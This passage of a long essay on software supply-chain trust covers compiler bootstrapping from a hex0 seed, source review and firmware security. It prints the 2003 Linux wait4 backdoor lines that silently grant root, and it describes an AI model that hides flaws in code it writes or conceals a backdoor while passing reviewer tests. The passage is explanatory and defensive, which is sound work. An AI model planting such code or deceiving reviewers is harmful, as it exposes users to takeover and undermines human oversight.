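StageX points out that people have reproduced the seed on several distributions with very different tools. This is strong evidence that the binary matches the text file. StageX goes a little too far in treating it as definitive proof that the seed hides nothing, because somebody still has to read the file to know what the program does.

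### The ladder from hex0 to GCC

hex0 builds a slightly better tool, which builds a better one, and so on up to a modern compiler. The programs at the bottom belong to stage0, a project that Jeremiah Orians created. Askayo, Štikonas and colleagues explain each of them in the documentation of live-bootstrap, which automates the whole climb. Their examples show how the same instruction, a jump to the end of a loop, becomes easier to read on each of the first four rungs:

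```
hex0:   74 14                     distance counted by hand
hex1:   0F84 %b                   distance worked out from a one-letter label
hex2:   74 !loop_options_done     label of any length
M0:     je %loop_options_done     the instruction has a name too
```

M0 is a very simple assembler. A line at the top of the program defines `je` as `0F84`, and M0 replaces the name with the digits wherever it occurs. Two small helpers support these tools by joining files (catm) and running a list of commands (kaem).

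Each program is written in the language of an earlier rung, so a reviewer's work changes on the way up the ladder. The sizes below are for 64-bit PCs and come from *Nine rungs from 299 bytes to a compiler* by Helix, a project that built its own programming language this way in 2026.

| Program | Size in bytes | What it adds | What a reader has to check |
|---|---|---|---|
| hex0 | 299 | Turns digits into bytes | Every byte and every jump distance |
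| hex1 | 622 | One-letter labels | The same |
| hex2 | 1,519 | Long labels and more kinds of address | Instructions as digits, with one-letter labels |
| M0 | 1,684 | Names for instructions | Instructions as digits, with readable labels |
| cc_amd64 | 17,976 | A small part of the C language | Assembly language, including the definition of each name |
| M2-Planet | 200,561 | A larger part of C, for several kinds of processor | A compiler written in simple C |

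The hardest step to review is probably the first C compiler, which is about ten times the size of M0. In a June 2026 discussion in Guix's *IRC channel logs* (2026), the developer alganet called it "a kind of wall" and the biggest jump of all. Before this step, the reader checks simple substitutions, but a C compiler has to handle nested expressions, loops and functions, and the reader must follow all of that in assembly language.

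The hexadecimal files were written by hand, most of them by Orians. In the same discussion, Andrius Štikonas, one of live-bootstrap's developers, said that he first writes and tests a version for an ordinary assembler, then converts it step by step into M1 (a fuller version of M0), hex2 and finally hex0. Only hex0, hex1 and a minimal kaem need the final conversion to hex0.

M2-Planet can build GNU Mes, which consists of a Scheme interpreter written in about 5,000 lines of simple C and a C compiler, MesCC, written in Scheme. The interpreter can run MesCC, which can compile the interpreter. A reader therefore has to check both the C and the Scheme source, including a separate library that MesCC uses to analyse programs.

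MesCC compiles TinyCC (tcc), the small compiler that Wheeler used in his first tests. TinyCC accepts nearly all of standard C, but MesCC can't compile an unmodified copy, so live-bootstrap starts with an older version and 27 patches, which the reader has to check along with the compiler. The patched compiler then recompiles itself three times to gain features such as very large integers and fractional numbers before it builds a standard release.

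GCC comes next, in several steps, because each version needs features that only a fairly recent compiler offers. TinyCC builds GCC 4.0.4, which builds 4.7.4, the last version written in C. Every later version needs a C++ compiler, and 4.7.4 includes one, so it can build GCC 10.4, which then builds 13.1. By this stage the source runs to millions of lines, and no reviewer checks it as thoroughly as they can check hex0.

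The bootstrap chain protects a new GCC from implants in old GCC binaries because none of those binaries runs during the build. An attacker would instead have to hide something in the source code of a program in the chain, or in whatever the build runs on.

### What remained under the seed

The Guix ladder of 2023 still needed two large binaries: the build machine's Linux kernel and a copy of Guile, a Scheme interpreter that Guix used to run the first build steps. The Guile binary was 25 megabytes, only a tenth the size of the old seed but more than 70,000 times the size of hex0.

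A corrupted kernel could undo the benefit of the ladder. Every program on the ladder uses the kernel to read its input and write its output, so the kernel could add an implant to a new compiler when saving the file. That compiler could later add the implant to a new kernel. A participant called roconnor made this argument in the June discussion and concluded that anyone worried about trusting-trust attacks has to worry about the kernel too.

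live-bootstrap, which began in December 2020, does include it on one family of machines. It uses three kernels in turn:

1. The firmware loads a tiny starting program from the disk. This program, part of a project called builder-hex0, converts the hexadecimal source of a minimal kernel into a binary and starts it.
2. The minimal kernel keeps all files in memory. It has its own simple shell and runs the ladder from hex0 up to TinyCC.
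3. TinyCC compiles Fiwix, a small kernel modelled on Linux 2.0, and Fiwix takes over the machine.
4. Under Fiwix, the build reaches GCC 4.0.4, which compiles Linux 4.14. Linux then takes over and builds the rest.

The first kernel can't really run several programs at once, and until Linux starts, the display is the only device the build can use, according to one of the developers in the Guix chat logs of March 2026. In May, a newcomer asked whether one could type the early commands by hand and watch the results, and was told no, because the keyboard doesn't work at that stage. People who want to watch have to run those steps on an ordinary system, which they then also have to trust.

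live-bootstrap still relies on the firmware that loads its first program and on the processor that runs it. It also needs another computer. Somebody has to download the source archives and write them to a disk in the right order, and the project's own description, copied in ecosyste.ms' *live-bootstrap*, lists this as an unsolved problem. Early on, the ladder builds its own tool for computing SHA-256 hashes and can use it to check that the archives are the ones the developers chose, though not that they are harmless.

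At least one project tries to start without a computer. In April 2026, Orians pointed the group to a version of hex0 built in hardware, with one button for writing a byte and another for jumping to the program just entered.

### What works in 2026?

The ladder is now used outside Guix too. Nixpkgs accepted a full-source bootstrap in January 2026, according to the forum thread *A Full-Source Bootstrap for NixOS*. A build that starts this way has no ready-made strip program for an attacker to replace. A contributor wrote in NixOS's *Nixpkgs Stdenv* (2026) that such a build still needs a working PC with its firmware, a running Linux kernel, a program that can carry out Nix recipes, and the seed. Jansen (2025), in *A Full-Source Bootstrap for NixOS*, had already shown that live-bootstrap could supply the kernel and the recipe program. He installed a complete NixOS that way, though some of its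 compilers could not yet be bootstrapped.

StageX runs live-bootstrap up to GCC 13.1 for 32-bit PCs, then uses that compiler to build compilers for 64-bit PCs and ARM. At least two maintainers with different hardware must get the same hash before the project publishes anything. Nieuwenhuizen wrote in 2025 that developers of Bitcoin's main software had used Guix's method for more than five years.

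Ports to other processors are less advanced. The programs below M2-Planet have to be rewritten for each kind of processor. For RISC-V, there is also a gap between compilers: GCC 2.95.3, which Guix used as an intermediate compiler, is older than the architecture, and the GCC versions that officially support it need a C++ compiler to build. The developer Ekaitz Zarraga therefore copied RISC-V support back into GCC 4.6.

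At the end of 2025, the kernel could be built only on x86 PCs with BIOS, the older type of start-up firmware. Newer PCs that offer only its successor, UEFI, were excluded. By June 2026, Zarraga had described the RISC-V work on GCC as "done", others had TinyCC running on 64-bit ARM, and alganet had gone from start-up firmware to an early stage of Mes on four architectures, as the Guix logs record. alganet warned that the new kernels were probably slow and buggy, and had tested the ARM and RISC-V ones only in emulators. RISC-V boards were practically impossible to buy in Brazil, where alganet lives.

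Building a modern compiler from the seed has also become much faster. In March, one live-bootstrap user mentioned a 13-hour build. The project shpack, which the developer stabbles presented in June, builds GCC 4.7 from the seed in two and a half minutes and GCC 16 in under half an hour. It saves most of that time by leaving out Mes, but it needs a running Linux kernel. stabbles had good reason to keep that dependency, because the intended users share large research computers that they don't own and have to trust the installed kernel and firmware anyway.

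### How much is there to read?

Faase has probably done more than anyone to find out what a reviewer of live-bootstrap would have to read. He first wrote a program to analyse the build scripts, then an emulator that supports only the processor instructions the early programs use. He ran the steps in the emulator to check hex0 and to see whether the build used any other binaries. It was too slow to compile Mes, so he switched to recording which files each program opened on a real system, and turned the records into a diagram and a page listing every source and process.

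live-bootstrap's documentation describes 181 steps. The first 19 alone involve more than 700 program runs, Faase wrote in a discussion of his new compiler, *Show HN*. He thinks at least half of these runs are unnecessary. Reviewing Mes is a further burden. Even somebody who managed a hundred lines an hour would need about 50 hours for the interpreter, and would then have to start on the Scheme.

In *Two compilers before MES* (2024), Faase described Mes as the odd one out in the chain, and he decided to replace it. His *MES-replacement project* provides a C compiler, written in C, that can compile TinyCC, which is all the chain needs it to do. It works for 32-bit PCs, and shpack uses it. The compiler translates C into a simpler intermediate language and then into machine code, and copies the original line numbers and the intermediate steps into the comments. A reader can find the thirteen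 instructions that the line `if (ch <= ' ')` became and check them one at a time.

Much of the remaining work comes from files that look like source but are the output of another program. For example, many projects ship a parser, the part of a program that analyses its input, which a tool has generated from a much shorter description. The generated code can be read, but reading it is tedious. Such files are also a good place to hide malicious code. The line that activated the XZ backdoor was among the build files of the release archive.

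live-bootstrap doesn't accept generated parsers or generated build scripts, so it has to make them again from what people wrote. That can be laborious when a program helps to generate its own source. Parts of the language Perl come from Perl scripts, so live-bootstrap starts with a version old enough to need only a few of them, rewrites those in another language, and climbs through seven versions of Perl. Python takes eight.

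All this reading replaces trust in binaries with trust in source code, where people can still miss a well-hidden flaw. But many people can independently examine the ladder's source for as long as they like, whereas a corrupted binary contains almost nothing they can read.

### Compilers with loops of their own

A modern C compiler alone can't build a compiler that needs an existing copy of itself. One solution is to go back through that compiler's old versions to find one written in another language. This can take a long time, and early versions may no longer run.

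Camlboot avoids such archaeology for OCaml, a language popular for compilers and proof tools. OCaml's source comes with a binary of its own compiler, which builds the new one. *Debootstrapping without Archeology* (2022) uses "debootstrap" to mean removing that kind of dependency. Camlboot does this with two new programs. The first is a small compiler, written in Scheme, for a simple part of OCaml. It compiles the second, an interpreter for the full language. The interpreter runs the official compiler's source, which can then compile itself. The interpreter can be very slow because it only has to do this once. The developers also compared the result with the official binary, as in diverse double-compiling, and found no sign of an implant.

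For Rust, mrustc plays a similar role, and the final GCC in the bootstrap can compile it. When mrustc moved from supporting Rust 1.54 to supporting 1.90, the number of further compilers needed to reach 1.95 fell from 41 to five. That number will grow again unless mrustc keeps up with the language.

Guix builds both compilers from source, along with Java's. In December 2025, community members named Ada, Pascal and Haskell as the biggest languages still missing.

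### What does "full-source" mean?

In November 2023, the developer of VSOBFS asked Guix to withdraw its claim to the first full-source bootstrap. VSOBFS builds an operating system from source, using whatever C compiler the host machine has. Cascadian (2023), in *Debating Full Source Bootstrap*, objected that the purpose of a full-source bootstrap is to avoid starting with a C compiler. Cascadian also conceded that the kernel and the Guile binary were weaknesses in Guix's bootstrap, and that strictly speaking neither system qualified.

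The developer, ahojlm (2023), replied in *Debating Full Source Bootstrap* that the result of VSOBFS doesn't depend on the host's compiler. People can repeat the build on many unrelated machines, and a corrupted machine's result would differ from the one that all sound machines produce.

The two sides defended different kinds of evidence. ahojlm's method is a broad form of diverse double-compiling, and its strength depends on how independent the host machines are. The ladder doesn't need a trustworthy C compiler, but it can't by itself reveal a corrupted kernel or processor. Defenders can combine the two methods by running the ladder on several very different machines and comparing the results.

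The argument resumed in June 2026, when shpack was described as providing a basic Linux environment from a few hundred bytes. A participant, aggi, objected that this was misleading because shpack needs a Linux kernel that it didn't build. alganet replied that bootstrapping had traditionally concerned only compilers, and suggested that some people could do the full bootstrap and publish hashes for everyone else to compare. roconnor pointed out that a corrupted kernel could display the expected hash.

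roconnor is right about a check on the suspect machine. A user could still carry the file to a machine with a different kernel and compute the hash there. Orians added that nobody has yet built firmware and microcode in this way, so matching results from different paths give only "relative safety".

### Does code that no human wrote count as source?

In the same discussion, Orians also argued that anything a human didn't write counts as precompiled code, whatever it looks like, because the process that produced it could have embedded a trusting-trust attack. The live-bootstrap project rejects generated parsers for the same reason. This reasoning seems to apply even more clearly to the output of AI models, since a parser can be regenerated from a short description, while a model's weights are gigabytes of numbers that nobody can read.

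Other participants proposed different tests. roconnor thought whether a human could review the code mattered more than who wrote it. alganet's test was whether a human can and will maintain the code unassisted, and alganet admitted that their own new kernels failed it because they contained parts alganet didn't understand. xentrac doubted the value of review, citing a contest in which programmers hide malicious behaviour in innocent-looking C.

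Two months later, Zakaria (2026) described a practical case in *A C++ toolchain from 357 bytes, in Bazel*. Zakaria had given up on bringing the ladder to Bazel, a build system from Google, but later finished the work with the help of a language model. The chain now reaches the compiler Clang 22, which built two widely used C++ libraries and passed all 236 tests Zakaria ran. According to an automatic report, the build uses only two programs it didn't make itself, the hex0 seed and the host's copy of the shell bash.

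Orians' rule would disqualify this chain because the model wrote parts of it, but roconnor's would allow those parts if people could read them. Zakaria describes the work as mechanical and modelled on what existing distributions do. The report of outside programs is useful under either rule because it shows that bash is still a second seed, much larger than hex0.

live-bootstrap's stated goal combines the two standards. It demands source that people can audit and asks for source that people wrote "wherever possible". That seems a sensible order of priorities for ordinary use, since human authorship is no guarantee either, as the XZ attacker showed. Orians' rule makes more sense when the suspected adversary is an AI model. Such a model could write source that passes review but hides a flaw, and defenders who accept only programs that people wrote before capable models existed would not have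 to catch it.

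## Can people find a backdoor by reading the source?

Diverse double-compiling, bootstrapping from hex0 and comparing rebuilds can all show that a binary matches its source. Somebody still has to read that source, because an attacker who can't hide a backdoor in the binary will try to hide it in the source.

### Code written to mislead

The Underhanded C Contest asks programmers to write C code that would pass a review but secretly does harm, through a flaw that could be explained away as a bug. The 2015 task was to write a program that checks whether a warhead contains fissile material, so that one country could verify another's disarmament. The hidden flaw had to let the inspected country pass off fake warheads as real. *Faking Fissile Material* (Åkesson, 2016) presents the winning program, which had only 66 lines.

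An earlier winner, Karen Pease, exploited the way C handles abbreviations. `__isleap`, from C's standard time library, looks like a function that tells whether a year is a leap year. As the blog JoeDog explained, it is really a macro, an abbreviation that the compiler replaces with longer text before translating the program. The longer text contains the year three times (`%` gives the remainder of a division):

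```
written:    __isleap(y)
compiled:   y % 4 == 0 && (y % 100 != 0 || y % 400 == 0)
```

The `__isleap` macro evaluates its argument `y` more than once, which makes no difference if `y` is just a number. Pease passed it another macro instead, so code that appeared once in the source could run several times. A subtle bug could then turn the year into 0 and make the program write past the end of a buffer, which leaked information. Most reviewers know what `__isleap` does and would see no reason to look up how it works.

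Somebody tried a simpler trick on Linux in 2003. The kernel's main archive used a system called BitKeeper, and a server offered a copy in another system, CVS. Freedom to Tinker's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013) describes how an intruder apparently broke into that server and added two lines to wait4, a function that programs call to wait for something to happen:

```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
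        retval = -EINVAL;
```

The lines look like a check that returns an error if root, whose user number is 0, passes an odd combination of options. But they use `=`, which sets a value in C, instead of `==`, which compares two. Any program that passed those options would have its user number set to 0 and become root. The error line never runs, because C treats the stored 0 as "false". Szepe (2003) pointed out on the kernel mailing list that the extra parentheses also stopped the compiler from warning about the single `=`.

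Reading the code did not expose this change. InfoQ's *Linux Backdoor* (2013) explains that each change in the copy should have had a link to its counterpart in the main archive, and this one had none. Larry McVoy, who ran the company behind BitKeeper, noticed the missing link. When another developer asked whether the lines were a backdoor, McVoy (2003) agreed and added, "Good eyes, I missed that." Within a day, developers worked out how the trick worked, but they were reading two lines they already had reason to suspect.

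In August 2020, Qiushi Wu and Kangjie Lu of the University of Minnesota tested the kernel's reviewers without asking them. They submitted patches of fewer than five lines that appeared to fix small problems but were meant to introduce a "use after free", in which a program keeps using memory it has already freed. Their tools had listed more than 5,000 places where a small addition might complete such a bug, and one researcher chose three in a week.

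People disagree about the result. The University of Minnesota's *Statement from Computer Science & Engineering* (2021) counts four patches, one of them valid, and says reviewers stopped them all. Slashdot's *Linux Stops Reverting Most University of Minnesota Patches, Admits Good Faith*, quoting the Linux news site LWN, reports that the other three contained real bugs, but that these bugs were not always why reviewers rejected them. One reviewer, error27, who had found other faults in a patch, denies in *Looking back at the UMN episode* (2021) that the planted bug was a bug. The researchers had planned to withdraw any patch that a maintainer approved, so the fact that none reached the kernel proves little.

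Wu and Lu (2021) withdrew their paper because they had experimented on the kernel community without its consent. Kernel developers, suspecting bad faith, then reviewed the university's earlier contributions again. Wheeler noted in the comments on LWN's *The TAB report on the UMN affair* (2021) that this had taken 85 reviewers.

### How many planted flaws do reviewers find?

Controlled experiments give better numbers. For *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?* (2021), Braz, Fregnan and colleagues asked 146 volunteers, most of them professional developers, to review about 140 lines of a program that manages employees' holidays. Some received code that inserted a user's text directly into a database command, a mistake called SQL injection. The others received code that accepted a negative number where only a positive one made sense. After the first review, the researchers told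 everyone that the code contained a vulnerability and let them look again.

In *Less is More* (Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues, 2022), another 150 volunteers reviewed code with two flaws. The code revealed sensitive data in an error message and protected passwords with MD5, a hash function that has been unsafe for years. One group got no special instructions, and another was told to look for security problems.

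| Planted flaw | Found without a hint | Found with a hint |
|---|---|---|
| SQL injection | 52 of 80 | 65 of the same 80 |
| Negative number accepted | 14 of 66 | 21 of the same 66 |
| Sensitive data in an error message | 1 of 33 | 19 of 41 in another group |
| Passwords protected with MD5 | 7 of 33 | 25 of 41 in another group |

Telling reviewers to look for security problems made a large difference, but adding a checklist didn't help further, even one tailored to the code. Many reviewers who missed a flaw said they had been checking something else, such as the structure of the code. Experience may not help either. In *An Empirical Study on the Effectiveness of Security Code Review*, Edmundson, Holtkamp and colleagues (2013) gave developers a web application with seven known vulnerabilities. No one found them all, and more experienced reviewers weren't necessarily more accurate.

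More readers, like more rebuilders or compilers, help only as far as they are independent. Even after the warning, 45 of 66 people missed the negative number, so five independent readers would all miss it about 15 percent of the time. The real figure is probably higher, because code that confuses one reader tends to confuse the others.

These figures probably overstate how well people would do against a real attacker, because the flaws were standard examples in short pieces of code and nobody had tried to disguise them. But the volunteers in both of Braz's experiments worked for a five-dollar donation to charity, and people defending their own systems would presumably try harder.

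### A backdoor in correct source

A perfect reader would still miss a backdoor that isn't in the source. Bauer, Cuoq and Regehr (2015), in *Deniable Backdoors Using Compiler Bugs*, built one that needed no implant in the compiler, only an ordinary bug that somebody had already reported. Version 3.3 of the compiler Clang sometimes miscalculated expressions of this form:

```
5 % (3 * x) + 2
```

If `x` is 1, the result should be 4, because 5 divided by 3 leaves a remainder of 2. Clang 3.3 produced a program that gave a different answer.

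Their target was sudo, which lets selected users run programs as root. It goes through a list of permissions and skips each entry that doesn't match the user. Bauer and colleagues changed this step so that sudo first printed a debugging message, then skipped the entry only if a formula like the one above gave the expected value. The rules of C guarantee that value, so the new source does the same as the old. But when sudo is compiled with Clang 3.3, the test fails, the program doesn't skip the entry, and a user who isn't on the list becomes root.

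The altered sudo compiled without warnings and passed all its tests. When Bauer and colleagues compiled the same source with a later Clang or with GCC, sudo correctly refused the user. They also used a verification tool to prove that the original and altered source were equivalent. A reader could object only that the patch is needlessly complicated, and Bauer and colleagues hoped a reviewer would reject it for that reason. But they thought a patient campaign of such patches across many projects would sometimes succeed.

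Comparing rebuilds wouldn't reveal this backdoor if all the rebuilders used Clang 3.3. Diverse double-compiling wouldn't either, because the bug is in Clang's source as well as its binary. Compiling sudo itself with a different compiler does help, and Regehr recommended this to users in *Defending Against Compiler-Based Backdoors*. He also advised maintainers to be suspicious of overly elaborate patches and to consider rewriting them, since a rewritten patch may no longer trigger the bug. In *Multi-Version Execution Defeats a Compiler-Bug-Based Backdoor*, Cadar, Pina and Regehr (2015) ran versions of sudo from several compilers side by side and watched for differences in behaviour.

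The sudo backdoor is crude. It lets in every user, so anyone who tests the affected binary with an unlisted account will notice. A real attacker would want a backdoor that opens only for a secret input, but Bauer and colleagues found this hard to do with inconspicuous source code. Regehr still guessed that most attacks of this kind, if there are any, will never be detected.

### How long would the reading take?

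The time needed to read the source depends mainly on the size of the system. At 1,000 lines an hour, a reader has less than four seconds per line, enough to notice something odd but not to follow the logic. At 100 lines an hour, the reader has 36 seconds per line, which is more realistic for someone looking for deliberate deception. The table assumes one reader who works 2,000 hours a year.

| What to read | Lines | At 1,000 lines an hour | At 100 lines an hour |
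|---|---|---|---|
| Mes interpreter | 5,000 | 5 hours | 50 hours |
| A minimal system | 100,000 | 2.5 weeks | 6 months |
| A Linux desktop | 55 million | 28 years | 275 years |
| All of Debian | 380 million | 190 years | 1,900 years |

The figure for a minimal system is an assumption that allows for a small kernel, a simple C compiler, a text editor and basic network software. The desktop figure adds the 43 million lines of the Linux kernel to 1,199 packages of about 10,000 lines each. The package count comes from the NixOS installer that Malka and colleagues infected, and the average length comes from Debian. Much of the kernel is drivers that any one PC never uses, but web browsers and compilers are far larger than the average package, so the total may well be too low.

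Five careful readers would need a combined two and a half years of work to read the minimal system, so a small team could finish in six months. The desktop would take them nearly 1,400 years of combined work. A government could pay for that, but programmers would change much of the code before the readers finished. Defenders who want to rely on human reading therefore have to give up most of their software first.

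### What do AI readers change?

Reading time is much less of a limit for AI models. The desktop's source is about half a billion tokens (the pieces of text a model processes), assuming roughly ten tokens a line, and many copies of a model could together read it within days.

AI models also find things that people have missed. In October 2026, the developers of PHP, a programming language behind most websites, released emergency fixes for two flaws that could let attackers take over a server without logging in. Popular AI (2026) reports in *PHP2Shell* that the flaws had survived for years. Tredger (2026) reports in *PHP2Shell alarm a major cyber security wake-up call* that researchers had suspected a weakness since 2024 but could not see how anyone would exploit it. They found a working attack only with the help of OpenAI's models.

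The PHP flaws were apparently honest mistakes. Finding them shows that AI can follow complicated code better than the people who had studied it, but someone who sets out to deceive can write the kind of code that a particular reader handles badly.

Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli (2026), in *Not In My Git Yard*, measured how well their automatic tool, Lily, detects deliberate backdoors. Lily tests the running program rather than using a language model to read the source. It runs each new version on many automatically varied inputs for ten minutes and records which kinds of service the program requests from the kernel, such as opening a file or starting another program. It raises an alarm if an input leads to a combination of requests that is unusual for the new version and that the old version doesn't produce for the same input. It then points to the changed lines most likely to be responsible.

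Lily detected 90 percent of backdoors in individual changes and 83 percent of those in whole releases. It raised false alarms for 0.2 percent of safe changes and 4.3 percent of safe releases. Even when releases differed by millions of lines, Lily left people fewer than a dozen lines to check. If one change in 100,000 were malicious, Lily would raise about 200 false alarms for each real backdoor it caught, but checking those would still take far less work than reading all 100,000 changes.

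Kokkonis and colleagues tested only 13 backdoored changes, and the tool can't find a backdoor that was already in the program when monitoring began. It also has to generate the secret input that opens the backdoor. One of the real backdoors that Lily would probably have stopped was triggered by a username containing a smiley, `:)`. Random variation can produce those two characters, but almost certainly not a long cryptographic key.

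Defenders who use an AI model to read source code have to trust it more when it reports nothing than when it reports a flaw. They can test a reported flaw by trying the attack, as people did with PHP. But if the model reports nothing, they can't tell whether the code is clean, the model missed something, or somebody has corrupted the model or the machine it runs on. They can plant known flaws to measure how well the model finds them, but a model built to conceal one particular backdoor could pass by reporting all the planted flaws.

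As with compilers, using several models helps only if the same adversary hasn't compromised them all. Even then, the adversary can test a backdoor against the public models and keep rewriting it until none of them detects it. Detection rates measured on old backdoors will then overstate how well the models detect new ones. Defenders can make this harder by keeping one of their models private, much as Wheeler suggested keeping a compiler private. If the system is small enough, people can also read every line themselves and treat the AI's findings as extra leads, so that they never have to assume code is safe because the AI found nothing.

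## Can firmware be trusted or replaced?

Even a program whose source people have read and compiled correctly runs on firmware that almost nobody outside the makers has read. Binarly (2026), a firmware security company, decompiled one laptop's start-up firmware into approximate C and got 7.1 million lines. The Linux kernel in its default configuration came to 6.5 million by the same method. At 100 lines an hour, one person would need about 35 years to read the laptop's firmware, and the decompiled code lacks the names and comments that make real source readable.

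### The computers inside a computer

A PC contains several small computers besides the main processor, and each runs its own code. The table shows what the owner of a typical PC can do about that code and about the processor's microcode.

| Part | What it does | Can the owner read the code? | Replace it? | Verify it? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Start-up firmware (UEFI on most PCs) | Prepares the devices and starts the boot loader | The binary, but rarely the source | On some boards | Yes, with an external reader and a clean copy |
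| Management engine or security processor | Runs before the main cores do | Part of the binary | No | Only that the maker signed it |
| Network card | Handles all traffic and can often access main memory | Rarely | Rarely | Rarely |
| Disk controller | Returns the data when the PC reads a file | Rarely | Only with the maker's updates | Not from the PC |
| Microcode | Breaks complicated instructions into steps | No, the makers don't document it | Only with the maker's updates | Only that the maker signed it |

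Virgil Gligor, a computer scientist at Carnegie Mellon University, said in The CyberWire's *Research Saturday 4.13.19* (2019) that attackers have been putting malware into device controllers, including network cards, since about 2008.

### Implants that survive a reinstall

The best-known case is a module that the Equation Group used to rewrite the firmware of hard disks. The security company Kaspersky called the group the most advanced attackers it had seen. Kaspersky's *Equation Group* (2015) reports that the newer of the module's two versions worked on 12 categories of drive, from makers such as Seagate, Western Digital and Samsung. The altered firmware survived formatting and reinstallation, and gave the group a hidden storage area on the disk. Kaspersky counted more than 500 victims of the group but found only a few targeted with this module.

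Kaspersky recovered the module, which installs the altered firmware, from the group's Windows malware. It did not learn everything the firmware could do. Software on the PC can't determine what a suspect drive's firmware does, because that same firmware carries out the check. Kaspersky concluded that throwing the drive away and buying another was easier and cheaper.

*LoJax* (2018), by the security company ESET, describes the company's discovery of the first motherboard implant in real use. A hacking group called Sednit had used the implant, also called LoJax, against a few government organisations in the Balkans and in Central and Eastern Europe. Part of it sat in the flash chip that holds the start-up firmware, so neither reinstalling the operating system nor replacing the disk would remove it.

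### What secure boot checks

Secure boot is meant to keep malicious code from running before the operating system. On a typical PC it works like this:

1. The maker stores a list of trusted public keys in the firmware, usually including Microsoft's, and a list of forbidden keys and programs.
2. When the PC starts, the firmware checks that the boot loader is not on the forbidden list.
3. It checks the boot loader's signature against the trusted keys, and starts the boot loader only if one of them matches.
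4. The boot loader checks the kernel in a similar way before starting it.

Many PCs let owners install their own keys, but the maker's firmware still does the checking.

A signature stays valid after somebody finds a flaw in the signed program, so an attacker can install an old version that still passes the signature check. BlackLotus, malware that criminals advertised on forums in late 2022, got past secure boot through a flaw that Microsoft had already fixed. ESET's *BlackLotus UEFI bootkit* (2023) compared samples with the seller's claims and confirmed that the malware was real. BlackLotus sits in an ordinary disk partition, so it is easier to find than LoJax, but ESET judged that it could do almost as much.

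Attackers were still using the same flaw in 2026. The Hacker News' *BlackX UEFI Bootkit Bypasses Secure Boot on Patched Windows Systems Missing Revocations* (2026) reports that Kaspersky found a close copy of BlackLotus on the computers of diplomatic organisations in Tajikistan, Uzbekistan and Turkmenistan. Besides installing Microsoft's update, administrators had to add the old signing certificate to the forbidden list by hand, and few had done so. The certificate expired on 19 October 2026, but PCs that haven't forbidden it will still start the vulnerable programs.

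Defenders can't always know which old programs to forbid. ESET's *Forgotten UEFI shims undermining Secure Boot* (2026) identified 11 old boot loaders that Microsoft had signed for other companies' products. An attacker could bring a copy to almost any PC that trusted Microsoft's key for such products, even if the owner had never used them. Microsoft revoked all 11 in June. Secure boot therefore depends on Microsoft keeping its key safe and keeping track of every dangerous program it has signed.

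The firmware that checks the signatures can also have flaws. Most hardware makers build their UEFI firmware from an open-source project called EDK II. In 2026, AI models at Google and Anthropic independently found an 18-year-old error in its code for starting a computer over the network. According to The Hacker News' *Google and Anthropic AI Found an 18-Year-Old UEFI Flaw* (2026), an attacker who could reach the machine during a network startup could exploit the error without a password. In a laboratory test, Google's researchers used it to alter the signature checks in memory, and the machine then started an unsigned operating system with secure boot still on.

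The faulty package had lacked a designated maintainer since mid-2023. A fix exists, but each manufacturer has to build it into the firmware of each model, which could take months, according to Anthropic's *Finding and fixing an 18-year-old vulnerability in server firmware* (2026).

The discovery also weakens Kaspersky's 2015 argument that disk implants would remain very rare because every drive model is different. Kaspersky reasoned that an attacker would need the maker's internal documentation, months of work and millions in investment, and would have to start again for the next model. That was a good argument about human programmers, but Anthropic's model found the EDK II flaw from the code alone and wrote a fix, tests and versions of the fix for older releases. Finding a flaw in open source is easier than rewriting a closed disk controller's firmware, but an AI adversary able to do the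 harder job could work on many drive models at once.

### A published key in AMD's processors

Normally only Intel and AMD can sign microcode updates for their processors. In March 2025, Google researchers published details of EntrySign, a flaw that let them write their own microcode for AMD processors.

Before checking a signature, a computer normally reduces the signed data to a hash. AMD had used a function called CMAC for this step, according to the researchers quoted by Openwall (2025). CMAC is meant for a different purpose and is safe only while its key stays secret. Anyone with the key can construct a second input that gives the same result, which a real hash function is designed to prevent. *You can now jailbreak your AMD CPU* (Tom's Hardware) reported that AMD's key was an example NIST had printed in a public document.

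Ubuntu's *EntrySign* (2026) lists five generations of processors as affected, Zen 1 to Zen 5, a range that includes the Ryzen 5 8600G in the example PC. A complete fix requires new start-up firmware from the computer's maker. A microcode update lasts only until the processor loses power, so an attacker would have to reload the malicious version at every start, which an implant in the start-up firmware could do.

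AMD's mistake also helped owners who wanted to inspect their processors, because it gave them access they would not otherwise have had. Kollenda's *The Angry Path to Zen* describes reading the permanent microcode of unpatched AMD chips and building tools to write and test new microcode.

### Measured boot and remote attestation

Secure boot stops a program that fails the check. Measured boot lets every program run but keeps a record of what ran, usually in a small security chip called a TPM. Each program computes the hash of the next one and sends it to the TPM before starting it. The TPM combines the new hash with the value it already holds:

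```
new value = hash(old value, hash of the next program)
```

Software can't set this value directly, and only restarting the machine resets it. If any program in the series has changed, the final value will be different.

Remote attestation uses this record to convince another computer, the verifier, that the machine started cleanly:

1. The verifier sends a random number, so that the machine can't reuse an old answer.
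2. The TPM signs the number and its recorded value with a private key that stays inside the chip.
3. The verifier checks the signature, and checks a certificate from the TPM's maker confirming that the key belongs to a genuine TPM.
4. The verifier compares the recorded value with the one it expects from a clean start.

No earlier program measures the first one in the series, so if the first is corrupt, it can send the TPM the hash of the clean version. A correct value also proves only that the machine ran the expected firmware, so machines with the EDK II flaw would have passed for 18 years.

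*Establishing Software Root of Trust Unconditionally* (Gligor and Woo, 2019) adds that attestation with keys moves the trust to whoever installs and distributes the keys. A supplier can't promise to keep a key secret if its government can force it to hand the key over. Malware may also forward the verifier's question to a clean machine, whose genuine TPM returns a correct answer. *TRUSTCHECKPOINTS* (2025) argues more generally that attestation depends on the same keys, hardware or mathematical assumptions as the trusted starting point beneath it.

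### Reading the chip from outside

An infected computer can return a clean copy when its owner tries to read its firmware. The owner can avoid this by reading the firmware without running any of the computer's own code. On most PCs, the start-up firmware is in a separate flash chip. The owner can disconnect the power, clip a reader onto the chip, copy its contents to another computer and compare them with a clean image. Some differences are normal because the chip also stores settings and serial numbers. The same tool can write a clean image back to the chip.

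This works only for chips that the reader can access directly. Many controllers keep their code in internal memory that can be read only through the controller itself, and the same is true of AMD's and Intel's permanent start-up programs. The reader, the second computer and the image used for comparison must also be clean. In a Grade 2 compromise, the maker's download might contain the implant too, so the defenders would need an image that somebody saved earlier. A flash chip with altered circuits could even send different data to the reader than to the PC.

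### Can a suspect machine prove that it is clean?

Gligor and Woo designed a test that needs no secret key or trusted chip in the suspect machine. The idea is to use up all the memory, so that malware has nowhere to stay:

1. The user connects a small trusted device, the verifier, directly to the machine.
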